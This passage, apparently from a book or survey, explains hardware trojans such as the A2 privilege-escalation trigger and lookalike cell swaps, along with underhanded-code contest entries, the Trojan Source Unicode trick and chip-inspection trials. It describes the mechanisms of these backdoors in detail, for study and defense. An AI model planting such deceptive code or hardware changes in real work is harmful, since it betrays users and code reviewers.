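Doping changes can only alter existing circuits, so it is difficult to build a trigger with them. King's trojans had selective triggers but needed about a thousand gates. *A2* (Yang, Hicks and colleagues, 2016) describes a trojan that is both small and selectively triggered. The attacker works at the foundry, has only the finished layout, and cannot move existing parts or enlarge the chip. A company that prepares the layout could carry out the same attack more easily.

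A trigger that waits for many rare events has to count them. The trigger in *A2* does this with a capacitor, which stores charge, inside a single added cell. A digital version built for comparison took 91 cells.

The cell connects to a wire that seldom changes between 0 and 1. Each time the wire switches on, a small capacitor passes some charge to a larger one. If the larger capacitor is at voltage V₀, the transfer raises it by

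ΔV = C_unit × (V_DD − V₀) / (C_unit + C_main),

where V_DD is the supply voltage and C_unit and C_main are the sizes of the two capacitors. Suppose the main capacitor is nine times as large as the small one. Each transfer then closes a tenth of the remaining gap to the supply voltage, and, ignoring leakage, the main capacitor passes half the supply voltage on the seventh. At that point, a detector with its threshold at one half would fire.

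The capacitor also leaks charge constantly, so an occasional change on the wire has no lasting effect, and only a rapid burst of changes can fill it. When the burst ends, the charge drains and the trigger resets.

The researchers put the attack into the OR1200, another open-source processor. They chose the wire that signals a division by zero, which ordinary programs rarely do. A division by zero here sets a flag and the program carries on, so an attacker can repeat it hundreds of times in a loop. When the capacitor fills, one added logic gate changes the flip-flop that records whether the running program has ordinary or supervisor rights, which gives the attacker's program full control of the processor.

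They also built a stricter version with two capacitors, which fires only when signed and unsigned divisions alternate rapidly. Its payload changes a different bit, which they chose because it made success easy to check.

#### Why simulation misses it

Digital simulation treats every wire as either 0 or 1, so it can't represent the trigger's voltage, which rises in small steps. This is an example of the model gap described earlier. The attack shows up as a 1 where there should be a 0 only after the trigger has fired. A simulation of the original design would miss the attack anyway, because the foundry adds the cell later.

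The researchers designed the trigger with a circuit simulator, which calculates voltages. Simulating a whole processor this way for thousands of clock cycles is impractical, so they had to manufacture the chip to find out whether the complete attack worked.

#### Measurements on ten chips

The researchers had the processor manufactured with 65-nanometer technology and tested ten chips at six temperatures, from −25°C to 100°C. Both versions of the attack succeeded on every chip at every temperature. The researchers also used separate copies of the trigger, placed outside the processor, to count how many times a wire had to switch before the trigger fired.

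| Transistors in the trigger | Switching rate (MHz) | Cycles to fire, average measured | Cycles to fire, simulated |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary | 120 | 7.4 | 7 |
| Ordinary | 34.29 | 8.4 | 8 |
| Ordinary | 10.91 | 11.6 | 10 |
| Thicker insulation, less leakage | 120 | 12.6 | 14 |
| Thicker insulation, less leakage | 9.23 | 11.6 | 13 |
| Thicker insulation, less leakage | 1.88 | 13.5 | 12 |

At 10.91 MHz, the triggers in two of the ten chips with ordinary transistors failed to fire because charge leaked away too quickly. The simulator was less accurate about how long a trigger stayed on after the switching stopped. It predicted 25 microseconds for the version with thicker insulation, but the measured time was about 5. Still, an attacker could design a working trigger from simulation without first paying for a test chip.

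The attack also stayed hidden during ordinary use. The researchers ran five benchmark programs at all six temperatures, and none set off either trigger. Five programs are a small sample, and the group did not run a manufacturer's production tests. Even a test that set off a trigger might not reveal the attack, because most programs behave the same with supervisor rights as without them.

Measuring the chip's power is unlikely to reveal the trigger. The processor used 16 to 24 milliwatts while running the benchmarks, and repeated measurements varied by up to 3 microwatts. The researchers could only simulate the trigger's own consumption, which was at most half a microwatt. They also calculated that connecting the trigger delayed the chosen wire by about one picosecond, compared with a clock cycle of about 4,000 picoseconds.

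These experiments show that the trojan works, but not that a foundry could insert it unnoticed. Yang and colleagues prepared the processor's layout themselves, so they knew what each wire did. An attacker at a foundry would have to recover the circuit from the layout and then find the flip-flop that held the privilege bit. The researchers found it in a netlist without meaningful names by running programs that changed the bit at known times, which makes the search plausible for a small, publicly documented processor. They did not build a version for a modern desktop processor. They expected such a processor to offer more wires to choose from, but its duplicated arithmetic units might make the trigger less reliable.

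### Defenses against A2

Yang and colleagues concluded that the best defense would be trusted circuits that watch the processor while it runs. In *R2D2* (2018), Hou, He and colleagues proposed run-time detection specifically for *A2*, and their follow-up paper presents an on-chip framework for detecting analog trojans in microprocessors. *LATENT* (2025), which uses a language model to design analog trojans, describes one earlier detector that monitors wires under software control and another that looks for unusual spikes in current.

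A monitor that looks only for sudden activity on quiet wires could catch *A2*, which has to make a quiet wire unusually busy. The same monitor could miss DELTA, an extension of *A2* described in *SPICED* (2024), because DELTA generates its own short pulses and can connect to any wire, including a busy one. The foundry also makes the detector, and Becker and colleagues had warned before *A2* existed that an attacker could tamper with the detection circuit too.

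Another proposed defense is to fill a chip's unused space with working cells that a tester could check, so that an attacker has no room to add a trojan. Trippel, Shin and colleagues (2019) argue in *T-TER* that this can't stop a trojan as small as *A2*. Layouts typically fill only 60% to 80% of the available area because the wires need room, so a designer can't fill every gap.

*T-TER* protects the wires instead. To change the privilege bit, a trojan has to connect to a security-critical wire or run right next to one, so the designer surrounds those wires with guard wires. A foundry that removes or moves a guard wire changes the wire's electrical properties, which the customer can check by sending a pulse down it and comparing the reflection with what an intact wire should produce. Using software that assesses how an attacker could modify a layout, Trippel and colleagues found that the guard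 wires blocked *A2* with an overhead of about 1%.

The designer has to choose which wires to guard, and any wire left out gets no protection. A specification that omits a property has the same weakness. The method also covers only trojans that add parts. Trippel and colleagues knew of no trojan made by replacing existing parts that was both hard to detect and under the attacker's control, and they considered doping changes the closest case.

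A customer could also divide the work between two plants, so that the untrusted one never has the whole design. Usually the proposal is for a trusted plant to add some of the wiring and a cheaper, untrusted plant to make the transistors. Yang and colleagues object that *A2* attacks a flip-flop, which the untrusted plant would still make. They also cite research that recovered up to 96% of the missing wires by using knowledge of how layout software works. Moving nearly all the wiring to the trusted plant might stop the attack, but at the time nobody had manufactured a chip that way.

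### Trojans in standard cells

Two attacks from 2026 exploit the way designers assemble chips from standard cells, which are ready-made circuits such as gates and flip-flops. The netlist only names the cells, and a separate library describes their contents.

*An Automated Framework for Generating Stealthy Cell-Embedded Hardware Trojans* describes trojans hidden in the cell library, so the netlist can be correct even though one of the cells it names contains extra behavior. The researchers generated these trojans automatically for open-source benchmark circuits of several sizes. They conclude that checkers need to validate the cells as well as the connections between them.

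*Hardware Trojans from Invisible Inversions* describes a trojan made by swapping one unmodified library cell for another. Some cells with opposite functions look the same in electron microscope images taken from the back of the chip. One such pair is a buffer, which passes a signal on unchanged, and an inverter, which reverses it. An attacker who can edit the layout file on its way to the foundry can swap them without moving any wires.

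The researchers tried this on Ibex, a small open-source processor. Two swaps in a 28-nanometer version, or three in a 65-nanometer version, made the check on a program's privileges always succeed. They completed and simulated both layouts but manufactured neither. They could still judge how the cells would look, because an existing collection of microscope images showed nearly all of them in real chips.

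The trojan adds nothing to the chip, so there is no extra part to find and no new wire for *T-TER* to block. But it has no trigger, so any program that tries a forbidden operation will succeed, and a test that includes one should reveal the problem at once. The researchers acknowledge this and expect a version with a trigger to need many more swaps.

They also found a defense against the swaps, which was to have the design software avoid the nine cell types that made up the indistinguishable pairs in the 28-nanometer library. This made the chip 0.013% larger and increased its power use by 0.022%. An attacker could still insert one of the banned cells, but it would no longer look like the cell it replaced. The ban does not stop a foundry from changing the doping, an attack the researchers excluded from their analysis.

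## Contests in writing deceptive source code

The malicious part of underhanded code is in the source, where a reviewer can read every character, whereas the attacks on compilers and chips usually changed something that a reviewer of the source never saw. Wheeler warned about underhanded code in his dissertation, *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling* (2010). The method he proposed there can show that a compiler's binary matches its source, but the source can still mislead reviewers. Many public examples of underhanded code come from contests for writing it.

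### Miscounting votes on election day

Daniel Horn created the Obfuscated V Contest around the US presidential election of November 2, 2004. Entrants wrote a program to read a string of letters and count each K as a vote for Kerry, each B for Bush and each N for Nader. The program had to favor one candidate while looking as if it counted correctly.

The rules in Horn's *The Obfuscated V contest* let entrants write programs that miscounted votes all the time or only on election day. The organizers would run an election-day program on November 1, when it had to print the right totals. On November 2, judges would read the code and run the program that looked most correct, which won if it now miscounted. Horn offered bonus points for getting the total number of votes right. He later explained that a wrong result is harder to recognize when the numbers look about right.

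Paul Parkanzky won the election-day category. His program wrote out the day in words, and "second" is one letter longer than "first". On November 2, the longer message ran past the end of its allotted memory and changed the count in Bush's favor.

Michal Zalewski won the other category with a program that gave a tenth of the votes to Bush. It used a macro, a name that C replaces with a longer piece of text before compiling. Wheeler (2020) explains in *Initial Analysis of Underhanded Source Code* that the program used a variable `t` to point to the candidate who should receive the vote. The macro defined a second `t` that pointed to the first candidate on the list, and code inside the macro used this one instead. Each line looks reasonable, and a reader can find the fault only by working out which `t` a line refers to.

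### What the Underhanded C Contest rewarded

Scott Craver, an information security professor at Binghamton University, founded the Underhanded C Contest, which ran from 2005 to 2009 and from 2013 to 2015. In the contest's *FAQ*, he writes that Horn's contest impressed him because even a very short program could fail on only one day and so escape testing. For each contest, Craver set a simple data-processing task and a way to betray the user, such as shaving money from financial transactions.

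The rules in Craver (2016), *Results of the 2015 Underhanded C Contest*, favored short, readable programs. A trick of perception, such as the letter l in place of the digit 1, could score as high as one that used an obscure feature of C. An entry also scored higher if it looked innocent under syntax coloring, which shows comments, text and code in different colors. Entrants explained their trick in a separate file so the judges could first read the code without knowing the trick.

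Craver also gave more points to a flaw that its author could pass off as an honest mistake. The Underhanded C Contest's *The 2009 challenge* asked for bad behavior that was "plausibly deniable as a newbie coding mistake". Deniability helps a real attacker because a reviewer who finds the flaw still can't tell whether it was deliberate, so the attacker can correct it and try again later.

The 2009 task was to write a program that routes airline luggage but loses a bag when a check-in clerk types a certain kind of comment. Sam Blackburn's winning entry replaced swear words in the comments with milder versions, but a comma was missing from its list of replacements. C joins two pieces of text that have no comma between them, so the replacement for "damn" became nine characters long. The longer comment ran into the next part of the record, the part that marks the record as deleted. Blackburn could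 explain the missing comma as a typing error, and the clerk could claim not to know about the bug.

One runner-up checked for the character `0` instead of `\0`, which marks the end of a piece of text in C. As a result, a record disappeared if its comment began with a zero, as in "0ffered passenger compensation". Craver noted that the surrounding code was clumsy enough to make the bug look like a beginner's mistake.

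Making an attack deniable can reduce the attacker's control. An entrant who writes online as jmvalin built three triggers into one luggage program. One let the clerk add any record, but only by typing an obviously malicious comment. The most innocent-looking comment mentioned a flight canceled because of fog, and it could only make the program skip the next line of the file.

The contests show that skilled programmers can write such code, but they don't measure how often reviewers miss it. The judges knew that every entry was malicious, and they had no honest programs for comparison. Craver's site also describes mainly the winners and runners-up. Still, even a forewarned judge can miss a flaw. Craver recalls in *2014 Winners* (2015) that he stared at a very short entry by Domenico Andriole without finding the bug. The task was to write surveillance code for a social network that secretly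 alerts the people it watches. The lines Craver was reading contained no mistake. They saved a copy of the watched user's profile picture from a web address, and a user who controlled that address could see the request arrive.

The 2014 winner, Karen Pease, hid her attack in code that kept an audit record to prove that the surveillance followed the rules. The program checked for leap years with a macro that looked like a function. In this case, the macro ran the instruction passed to it three times, so the program wrote three entries to the audit record instead of one. The record overflowed, and the program erased the date on which the watched user's account was created.

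### The 2008 redaction program

The 2008 task was to write a program that blacked out rectangles in an image but let someone later recover part of what was there. Craver received more than 100 entries. Many scrambled the hidden pixels with a predictable random number generator or appended the original data to the end of the file. John Meacham won with a 55-line program that used neither method.

Meacham's program used the plain-text version of the PPM image format, which lists three numbers for each pixel, giving the amounts of red, green and blue. The numbers usually run from 0 for none to 255 for full brightness. The program went through the file one character at a time and replaced every digit inside the rectangle with a zero.

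| Original number | What the program wrote | Value an image viewer reads |
|---|---|---|
| 255 | 000 | 0 |
| 87 | 00 | 0 |
| 6 | 0 | 0 |

The rectangle looks completely black because an image viewer treats 000, 00 and 0 as the same number, but the file still shows how many digits each number had. On a scanned page, white paper gives three-digit numbers and dark ink gives one or two digits, so anyone who opens the file as text can make out the shapes of the letters. The file size doesn't change, so a checker who looked for added data would find none.

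Meacham's program has no trigger and leaks information every time it runs. A test that loaded the finished image and checked that every pixel in the rectangle was black would pass on any picture. The specification must also require that the output not depend on the hidden pixels. A checker could test this by redacting two pictures that differ only inside the rectangle, where one is white and the other black. The two output files should match byte for byte, but with this program they would not.

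### The 2015 warhead detector

For the 2015 contest, Craver worked with the Nuclear Threat Initiative, a nonprofit. In the task, two countries have agreed to destroy warheads, and inspectors need to confirm that each one contains fissile material. A scan produces a gamma-ray spectrum, which counts the rays detected at each energy. The spectrum would reveal secrets about the weapon's design, so the inspectors see only a "yes" or "no" from a program that compares it with a reference. Entrants had to write the comparison so that it worked properly in general but accepted a fake that the host country could arrange.

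About a third of the more than 40 entries relied on "not a number", the value a computer produces for an undefined calculation such as 0/0. Any ordinary comparison with this value counts as false, so a program that rejects a warhead only when its score is below a threshold will accept one with an undefined score. Most of these entries did poorly because C programmers are wary of any division without a check for zero, or because the host country could not realistically cause the undefined result.

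Other entries required tampering with the computer. In Stephen Oman's entry, setting the clock back during a scan gave the scan a negative duration, which made all the readings negative and let the fake pass. Inspection experts told Craver that they could not entirely rule out such tampering, but he still tended to prefer attacks that needed only an unusual test object.

The winner was Linus Åkesson, who had come third in 2008. In Åkesson, *Faking Fissile Material*, he describes the aim as secretly malicious code that would pass a review and whose behavior he could explain away as a bug. His program has 66 lines in three files. It checks that the test object gives off enough radiation in total, smooths both spectra to bring out their peaks, and compares them with a standard formula:

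similarity = Σ aᵢbᵢ / (√Σ aᵢ² × √Σ bᵢ²),

where aᵢ and bᵢ are the processed values of the two spectra at energy level i. Identical shapes give a similarity of 1.

The mistake is that two files use different definitions of `float_t`, a type of number. A shared header file, which holds definitions for the rest of the program, defines it as an 8-byte number, and the main file includes this header. The file that computes the similarity doesn't, and takes its definition from one of C's standard headers, where `float_t` is normally a 4-byte number. Each file makes sense by itself, but the main file passes a list of 8-byte numbers that the other file reads as 4-byte numbers.

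This helps a cheat because the comparison reads the right number of values but at half their proper size, so it covers only the left half of the spectrum.

It also distorts the sizes of the peaks, because the program treats each 8-byte number as two 4-byte numbers. Åkesson assumed that the whole-number counts in the spectrum stay below a million. Such numbers fit in one half of the 8 bytes and leave the other half zero, so every second value is zero in both spectra and doesn't affect the similarity. The remaining half becomes a much smaller number, because the 4-byte format has three fewer bits for the exponent, which sets a number's scale. Åkesson compares the effect to taking an eighth root. A value of 10 becomes about 2.6 and 1,000 becomes about 4.5, so a peak 100 times higher looks less than twice as high. The smoothing steps keep the values in a form that survives this conversion and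 push background noise below zero so the peaks stand out.

A host country could therefore leave a little fissile material in the fake to produce small peaks in the correct places, and add another radioactive substance whose peaks fall in the right half of the spectrum. The added substance supplies enough radiation to pass the first check, and the comparison then ignores it.

Åkesson tried this on 1,000 simulated materials. Each fake contained 10% of the real material and 90% of a random one with a strong peak on the right. Many fakes failed, but the host country needs only one that passes and can choose it in advance. One of his examples passed at any threshold up to 0.72.

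A reviewer who checked the formula would find nothing wrong with it. A simple rule that every file must include the header declaring its functions would have exposed the attack, because the compiler would have reported an error for the two conflicting definitions of `float_t`. The difficulty is adopting that rule before anyone knows that it matters. The announcement of the winner, the Nuclear Threat Initiative's *“Underhanded C” Contest Highlights Challenges For Nuclear Arms Control Verification Technologies*, notes that no standards existed for writing or reviewing arms control software.

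### Five countermeasures against 40 entries

Wheeler wanted to know how well simple tools and rules would work against such code. He started with the Obfuscated V entries because they were the earliest set available. Horn had published every program he scored, including two of Wheeler's own. Wheeler removed one program that contained no attack, which left 40. He sorted them by trick and chose five countermeasures, partly based on what he found.

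| Countermeasure | Main trick it targets | Entries with that trick |
|---|---|---|
| Address Sanitizer, a tool that monitors a program's use of memory as it runs | Reading or writing outside the allotted memory | 5 |
| Strict limits on macros | Macros that change what the code means | 9 |
| No lowercase l or capital O in names | Letters that look like the digits 1 and 0 | 7 |
| Syntax coloring and automatic reformatting | Working code made to look like a comment | 2 |
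| Extra warnings from the GCC compiler | `=` in place of `==`, and other common mistakes | 2 with `=` for `==` |

In C, `==` tests whether two values are equal, while `=` stores a new value. In 2003, someone tried to put a backdoor into the Linux kernel by writing `=` in place of `==`. GCC can warn about a single `=` inside a condition unless the programmer adds an extra pair of parentheses to show that it is deliberate.

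At least one of the five countermeasures caught 30 of the 40 entries. GCC should have warned about misleading indentation in another, but a compiler bug prevented it. Wheeler judged that six of the remaining nine, including one of his own, would make a reviewer suspicious, for example because they repeated large amounts of code.

Three entries were left. One set up only part of a table because it used the size of the wrong variable. Another treated a list of large numbers as a list of single bytes, much like Åkesson's later entry. The third accepted a lowercase "n" twice where it should have accepted "n" and "N". Wheeler thought that further compiler warnings could catch all three.

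The tools and the judges missed different entries. Horn's judges gave the two winners 7.0 and 7.3 out of 10, but GCC's warnings caught both. The three entries that the tools missed had scored 5.3, 4.3 and 3.7. A flaw that looks like a common mistake is easy to deny, but compiler developers have already written warnings for many common mistakes. An attacker who expects these tools to be used needs a plausible but unusual mistake.

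Wheeler also found that the organizers' description of the trick was wrong or incomplete in four cases, and he took this as a sign that such code is hard to understand even with a hint. The four cases are not equally strong evidence of this. The organizers did misread Ryan Cumings's entry. They blamed a swap of the letter O and the digit 0, but the main fault was a calculation that sent every vote to one of two rows. Travis Fisher's program was clean, and the attack was in the command that compiled it, which the organizers had not published. The published version of Geir Thomassen's program was the one without the attack. The fourth description was probably just badly worded.

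The result of 30 out of 40 has several limits. Wheeler chose the countermeasures after seeing the entries, as he acknowledges, so they might do worse on new entries. He ran GCC on every program but did not have time to run Address Sanitizer, so he judged what it would detect from how it works. He assessed the ban on lookalike letters without building a tool for it. All the programs were short pieces of C or C++, and he did not measure how often the countermeasures would raise false alarms on honest code.

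Address Sanitizer also has to be running when the fault occurs. Parkanzky's program overflowed its memory on November 2, so a test on November 1 would probably have shown nothing. GCC's warning was more useful here because it came from examining the code rather than running it.

The entrants in 2004 were trying to fool human judges, and nobody had told them to expect these tools. Wheeler recommends keeping some countermeasures secret so that attackers can't prepare for all of them. He also found the attacks easier to spot after reading several, and suggests training reviewers on examples. He could not be sure that practice was the reason, since the entries were sorted from hardest to easiest.

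### Contests in other languages and in cryptography

Wheeler also collected results from other contests, including a 2015 JavaScript contest that drew 34 valid entries. Many entries hid the malicious code in a block of encoded text that looked like a key. Several added a comment linking to Stack Overflow, a question-and-answer site for programmers. The organizer admitted that he found it easier to skip over code with a good comment above it. Neither trick depends on the kinds of mistake that compiler warnings usually cover.

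Entries in the Underhanded Crypto Contest, which ran from 2014 to 2018, are even harder for such tools to catch, because many of the winners exploited weaknesses in the cryptography itself. A compiler can warn about a suspicious use of `=`, but it can't detect that a method of generating keys is easy to break. The source can be clear and do exactly what it appears to do, like the generator described earlier that derives every 128-bit key from a 32-bit number. Wheeler did not analyze these entries in detail, but he concluded that specialists have to review this kind of code and that simple tools could at least save them time by catching the easier tricks.

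Changes to a programming language can also make deception harder. Solidity is a language for smart contracts, programs that hold and transfer money on blockchains such as Ethereum. Its developers studied the entries to a 2017 contest and then changed the language and its compiler. Wheeler quotes a 2017 account by Reitwiessner that identifies two common tricks.

One trick was to reuse a name built into the language, such as `now`, so that a reader would think the program used the current time when it used a value the attacker chose. The developers had added warnings about this shortly before the contest and were working to extend them. The other trick was to send money to a contract without running the code that records incoming payments. Reitwiessner thought this would be hard to prevent by changing the language. The developers also saw that a solver, a program that checks whether logical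 conditions can be met, could detect some of the attacks automatically.

### Trojan Source

*Trojan Source*, a 2021 paper by Boucher and Anderson, showed that the code a reviewer sees on the screen can differ from the code the compiler reads. Unicode, the standard that gives each character a number, includes invisible characters that control the direction of text, because Hebrew and Arabic run from right to left. Most compilers accepted these characters inside comments and quoted text, so an attacker could use them to rearrange a line on the screen without changing the order in which the compiler read it.

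Albini (2021), in *CVE-2021-42574*, gives an example in the language Rust. A reviewer sees this line:

`if access_level != "user" { // Check if admin`

The condition appears to compare the access level with "user", and the words after the two slashes appear to be a comment. In the file, the closing quotation mark comes after those words, so the compiler treats them as part of the quoted text. The program therefore compares the access level with a long phrase that no real access level would match. As a result, the condition is always true, and an ordinary user can run code meant for administrators.

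The same characters can make a working instruction look like part of a comment, or make a security check look active when the compiler ignores it. Boucher and Anderson built examples in 12 languages, including C, Java, Python and Solidity. They also defined two functions that both appeared to be called `sayHello`, one with a Latin H and the other with a Cyrillic letter that looks the same. The trick worked in ten of the languages, although Rust's compiler gave a warning.

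They contacted nineteen companies and organizations and gave them 99 days to respond before publication. Nine committed to releasing a fix. The responses varied because people disagreed about whether a compiler should deal with the problem.

| Software | Response |
|---|---|
| Rust | The compiler rejects the direction characters by default |
| GCC | The compiler warns by default about direction characters that lack a matching end character |
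| LLVM | A separate checking tool looks for the attack, but the compiler does not |
| Java | The developers made no change and considered it a problem for editors |
| GitHub | The website shows a warning and makes the characters visible |
| Visual Studio Code | The editor makes direction characters and possible lookalike letters visible |

GCC's developers wrote in GCC's *[PATCH] libcpp*, the message that introduced the compiler's warning, that the problem was not a compiler bug. A warning also has to be understandable. According to corbet (2022), in *Malcolm*, GCC developer David Malcolm tried the new warning on the published examples and had trouble understanding the results because the displayed code was still scrambled. He then added a way to mark warnings about the text encoding itself.

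Partial defenses may not help. Solidity's compiler already rejected some direction characters before 2021, but allowed a newer group that works just as well for the attack.

Nobody found a clear case of malicious use before the attack became public. GitHub searched more than a billion commits (recorded changes to code) from January to mid-October 2021 and found unmatched direction characters in 7,444. Almost all were harmless, and the few that resembled the attack included a security tool's test example. Albini's team searched every package version ever published in Rust's main library and found the characters in five packages, none of them malicious. A ban on unmatched direction characters would probably inconvenience few people, since fewer than one in 100,000 of the commits GitHub searched contained them.

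In April 2020, Wheeler had already suggested that projects could allow only ASCII characters (basic English letters, digits and symbols) in source code, although this was not among the five defenses he tried. This rule would have blocked both the invisible characters and the Cyrillic letter before anyone had published the attack. It works because it limits what an author may write, so the checker does not have to recognize each new trick. But it also prevents programmers from writing comments in Arabic, Hebrew or Russian, which is why Boucher and Anderson preferred to ban only direction characters without a matching end.

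The attack can also affect people who approve commands rather than review whole programs. *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* (2026) lists it as a threat to AI coding tools, because a user who approves a command with administrator rights may be approving something other than what the screen shows.

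## Trials of finding altered chips

Hardware researchers have measured how often checkers miss attacks and how often they raise false alarms, which the underhanded code contests did not do. In their trials, one team hides changes in a chip's design or layout, and another searches for them without knowing where they are.

### Comparing a chip with its layout

Puschner, Kison and colleagues (2023), in *Red Team vs. Blue Team*, checked four chips, made with 90, 65, 40 and 28 nanometer processes, against their layout files. Because nobody can add a trojan to a finished chip, the red team instead changed each chip's file at ten random positions. At four of these positions, the file showed filler where the chip had a working logic cell, so the cell looked as if it had been added to the chip. At the other six, the file named a different cell from the one on the chip, as if someone at the foundry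 had replaced it.

The blue team then compared each chip with its altered file:

1. It milled and etched away the silicon from the back of the chip until it reached the lowest layer, which contains the cells.
2. It took several thousand pictures of this layer with an electron microscope and joined them into one.
3. Software fitted the joined picture to the layout, correcting a slight distortion from the joining, and cut out a small picture of every cell.
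4. Where the layout showed filler, the software looked for vias, the vertical metal connections that appear as bright dots in working cells.
5. Everywhere else, it compared the cell with a reference picture of the same type and flagged any cell that looked too different.

| Chip | Cells in the layout | Changes found | False alarms | Hours of imaging |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 90 nm | 453,850 | 10 of 10 | 136 | 34 |
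| 65 nm | 571,060 | 10 of 10 | 6 | 23 |
| 40 nm | 917,819 | 10 of 10 | 15 | 53 |
| 28 nm | 1,467,851 | 7 of 10 | 360 | 36 |

The blue team found 37 of the 40 changes. All three misses were replaced cells on the 28 nm chip. Ruhr University Bochum's announcement of the results, *Detecting manipulations in microchips*, reports about 500 false alarms among more than 1.5 million cells. That cell count is lower than the 3.4 million in the table, probably because it leaves out filler cells.

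False alarms were rare by either count, but real changes were much rarer. The software raised about 14 false alarms for every change it found, and about 51 for every change it found on the 28 nm chip. Someone would have to look at all 554 flagged cells, which is manageable for four chips. Dust and debris caused 161 of the false alarms, and looking at the same pictures again can't settle those cases because the dirt covers the cells.

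The software found all 16 added cells, so a trojan like the ones King and colleagues built, with about a thousand extra gates, would be very hard to hide from this method. Replaced cells are the greater worry, and they were easier to find in this trial than in a real search because the red team picked its replacements at random.

### Swaps chosen by an attacker

*Hardware Trojans from Invisible Inversions*, the 2026 paper on swapping lookalike cells, began as a second analysis of the same images. The researchers wanted to know whether the misses at 28 nm came from poor image quality or from the cells themselves.

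The researchers reduced each cell to the positions of its vias. For each type of cell, the software aligned 50 copies from the chip, kept the vias that appeared in most of them, and averaged their positions. This removed dust and noise that affected only a few copies. The similarity of two types is the share of their vias that line up. For example, two versions of an OR gate have 16 vias between them, of which 12 line up, so their similarity is 12/16 = 0.75. The software flagged a cell if some other type fit it clearly better than the type named in the layout.

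| Chip | Replaced cells found, 2023 | False alarms, 2023 | Replaced cells found, 2026 | False alarms, 2026 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 90 nm | 6 of 6 | 136 | 6 of 6 | 30 |
| 65 nm | 6 of 6 | 6 | 6 of 6 | over 5,000 |
| 40 nm | 6 of 6 | 11 | 6 of 6 | 16 |
| 28 nm | 3 of 6 | 343 | 6 of 6 | 91 |

The new method found all 24 replaced cells, including the three that the blue team had missed. Its false alarm rate was high at 65 nm, where it misidentified bright flaws in the images as vias. The researchers recommend using both methods because the methods fail for different reasons.

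They then ran a harder test. For each chip, they took the ten pairs of cell types that looked most alike but did different jobs, and checked whether the software would notice one type replacing the other. At 90 nm, the 2023 method of comparing whole pictures missed almost every swap, although it had found all six random replacements on that chip. The new method caught nearly all of them, except swaps between XOR and XNOR gates, which give opposite outputs and have almost identical vias. The chip contains 3,106 copies of one and 5,192 of the other, so an attacker would have thousands of places to choose from. The 40 nm chip also had one pair that no method could tell apart, and the 28 nm chip had five.

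The university's announcement suggested that a clean room, specialized microscopes and machine learning would improve detection. The second analysis partly supports this, because better software found the three missed cells in the old pictures. But sharper pictures of the same layer won't distinguish two cells whose vias are in the same places. Imaging that shows doping might distinguish some of them, but it costs much more.

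### Destroyed samples and trusted layouts

Preparing a chip for this inspection destroys it, as does the polishing that reveals doping, so a customer can check only samples. If the foundry altered every chip, one sample is enough to reveal the change. But *Hardware Trojan Detection Using Unsupervised Deep Learning* (2022) describes a foundry that uses a separate mask to alter only a few chips in a batch of smart cards for bank logins. Even a few altered cards could be worth a lot of money to the attacker.

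Suppose 5 chips in a batch of 100 contain a trojan and the customer destroys 3 chosen at random. The chance that all 3 are clean is

(95/100) × (94/99) × (93/98) ≈ 86%.

The customer would have to destroy 45 of the 100 chips to have a 95% chance of including at least one altered chip. Imaging them at about 36 hours each would take roughly 1,600 hours of microscope time, and the inspection could still miss the change on an altered chip.

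Puschner and colleagues also assume that the original layout is free of backdoors, because their comparison checks only whether the chip matches the layout file. If a rogue designer or a tampered cell library put a trojan into that file, a foundry that follows it faithfully will manufacture the trojan, and the comparison will find no difference.

The 2023 software used a picture of the first copy of each cell type it found on the chip as the reference for the others, so a foundry that altered every copy of a type in the same way would have altered the reference too. Customers who can get the via positions from the library's own files could build their references from those instead, but they would then be trusting the library.

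### Leaving no room for a trojan

A customer could also rely on filling a chip's unused space, the defense described earlier. Knechtel, Eslami and colleagues (2025) tested this in a contest, described in *Trojan Insertion versus Layout Defenses for Modern ICs*. Fourteen teams registered and four qualified, with 23 designers between them. The teams had to protect the layouts of six encryption circuits in a 7 nm technology, while three experts tried to insert 36 different trojans, six per circuit.

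The defenders shrank the chips, filled gaps with extra working parts, and moved cells to break up the remaining free space. They could not use filler or spare cells, which an attacker can remove. Their layouts also had to meet every timing limit and manufacturing rule, because one broken rule can stop a foundry from making a chip.

The attackers used standard industry tools for making small, late changes to a layout. In the most aggressive mode, these tools first removed unnecessary buffers and shrank oversized gates, then moved the original cells to make room. This inserted every trojan into every protected layout, but usually broke timing or manufacturing rules. After the contest, the red team improved its techniques and tried again on the top three teams' layouts, testing 108 combinations of trojan and layout.

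| Attack techniques | No violations straight from the software | No violations after repairs by hand |
|---|---|---|
| Those used in the contest | 1 of 108 | about 45% |
| Those developed afterwards | 18 of 108 | about 84% |

The figures for repairs by hand seem to be partly estimates. The red team repaired some layouts and used a rule of thumb that more than 30 broken manufacturing rules were too many to fix.

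The winning team's layouts allowed no clean insertions with the contest techniques but 9 out of 36 with the new ones, more than either of the other two teams' layouts. The contest's score partly measured free regions of 20 or more adjacent sites, and on one circuit this team had removed all of them. The attackers still inserted a trojan there during the contest without breaking a manufacturing rule. Knechtel and colleagues conclude that earlier researchers were wrong to think a sufficiently full layout leaves no room for a trojan. The teams had filled up to about 95% of the available sites, and each trojan added less than 0.5% to the number of cells.

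The 84% measures whether a trojan fits, not whether it would go unnoticed. Nobody manufactured these chips, and the red team did not design its trojans to escape later tests. The organizers also told the red team which registers held secret data and what the timing limits were, which an engineer at a foundry might have to work out from the layout. But the software took only tens of minutes per attempt, so a rogue employee could insert a trojan without causing an obvious delay.

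### Power and timing fingerprints

Electrical measurements leave a chip intact, so a customer can apply them to every chip in a batch. Added gates draw power, and a gate attached to an existing wire slightly slows the signal on it. The customer measures some chips known to be clean, records the normal range as a fingerprint, and rejects any chip outside that range.

Altered chips are hard to find because no two clean chips are identical. Small differences in manufacturing change their power and speed, and Knechtel and colleagues note that this variation and measurement noise are a bigger problem in advanced technologies. Suppose the power of clean chips varies with a standard deviation of 2%, and a trojan adds 0.1%. A test that rejects 5% of clean chips would then reject only about 5.5% of altered ones. Repeating the measurement reduces the noise but doesn't remove the differences between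 chips.

Fingerprints work better against larger trojans. Electromagnetic measurements on a set of FPGAs had a better than 95% chance of detecting a trojan larger than 1.7% of the original circuit. The trojans in the layout contest were less than a third of that size, and King's processor trojans and the *A2* trigger were also far smaller than 1.7%. Measuring one small region at a time can help, since the trojan then makes up a larger share of the measured circuit.

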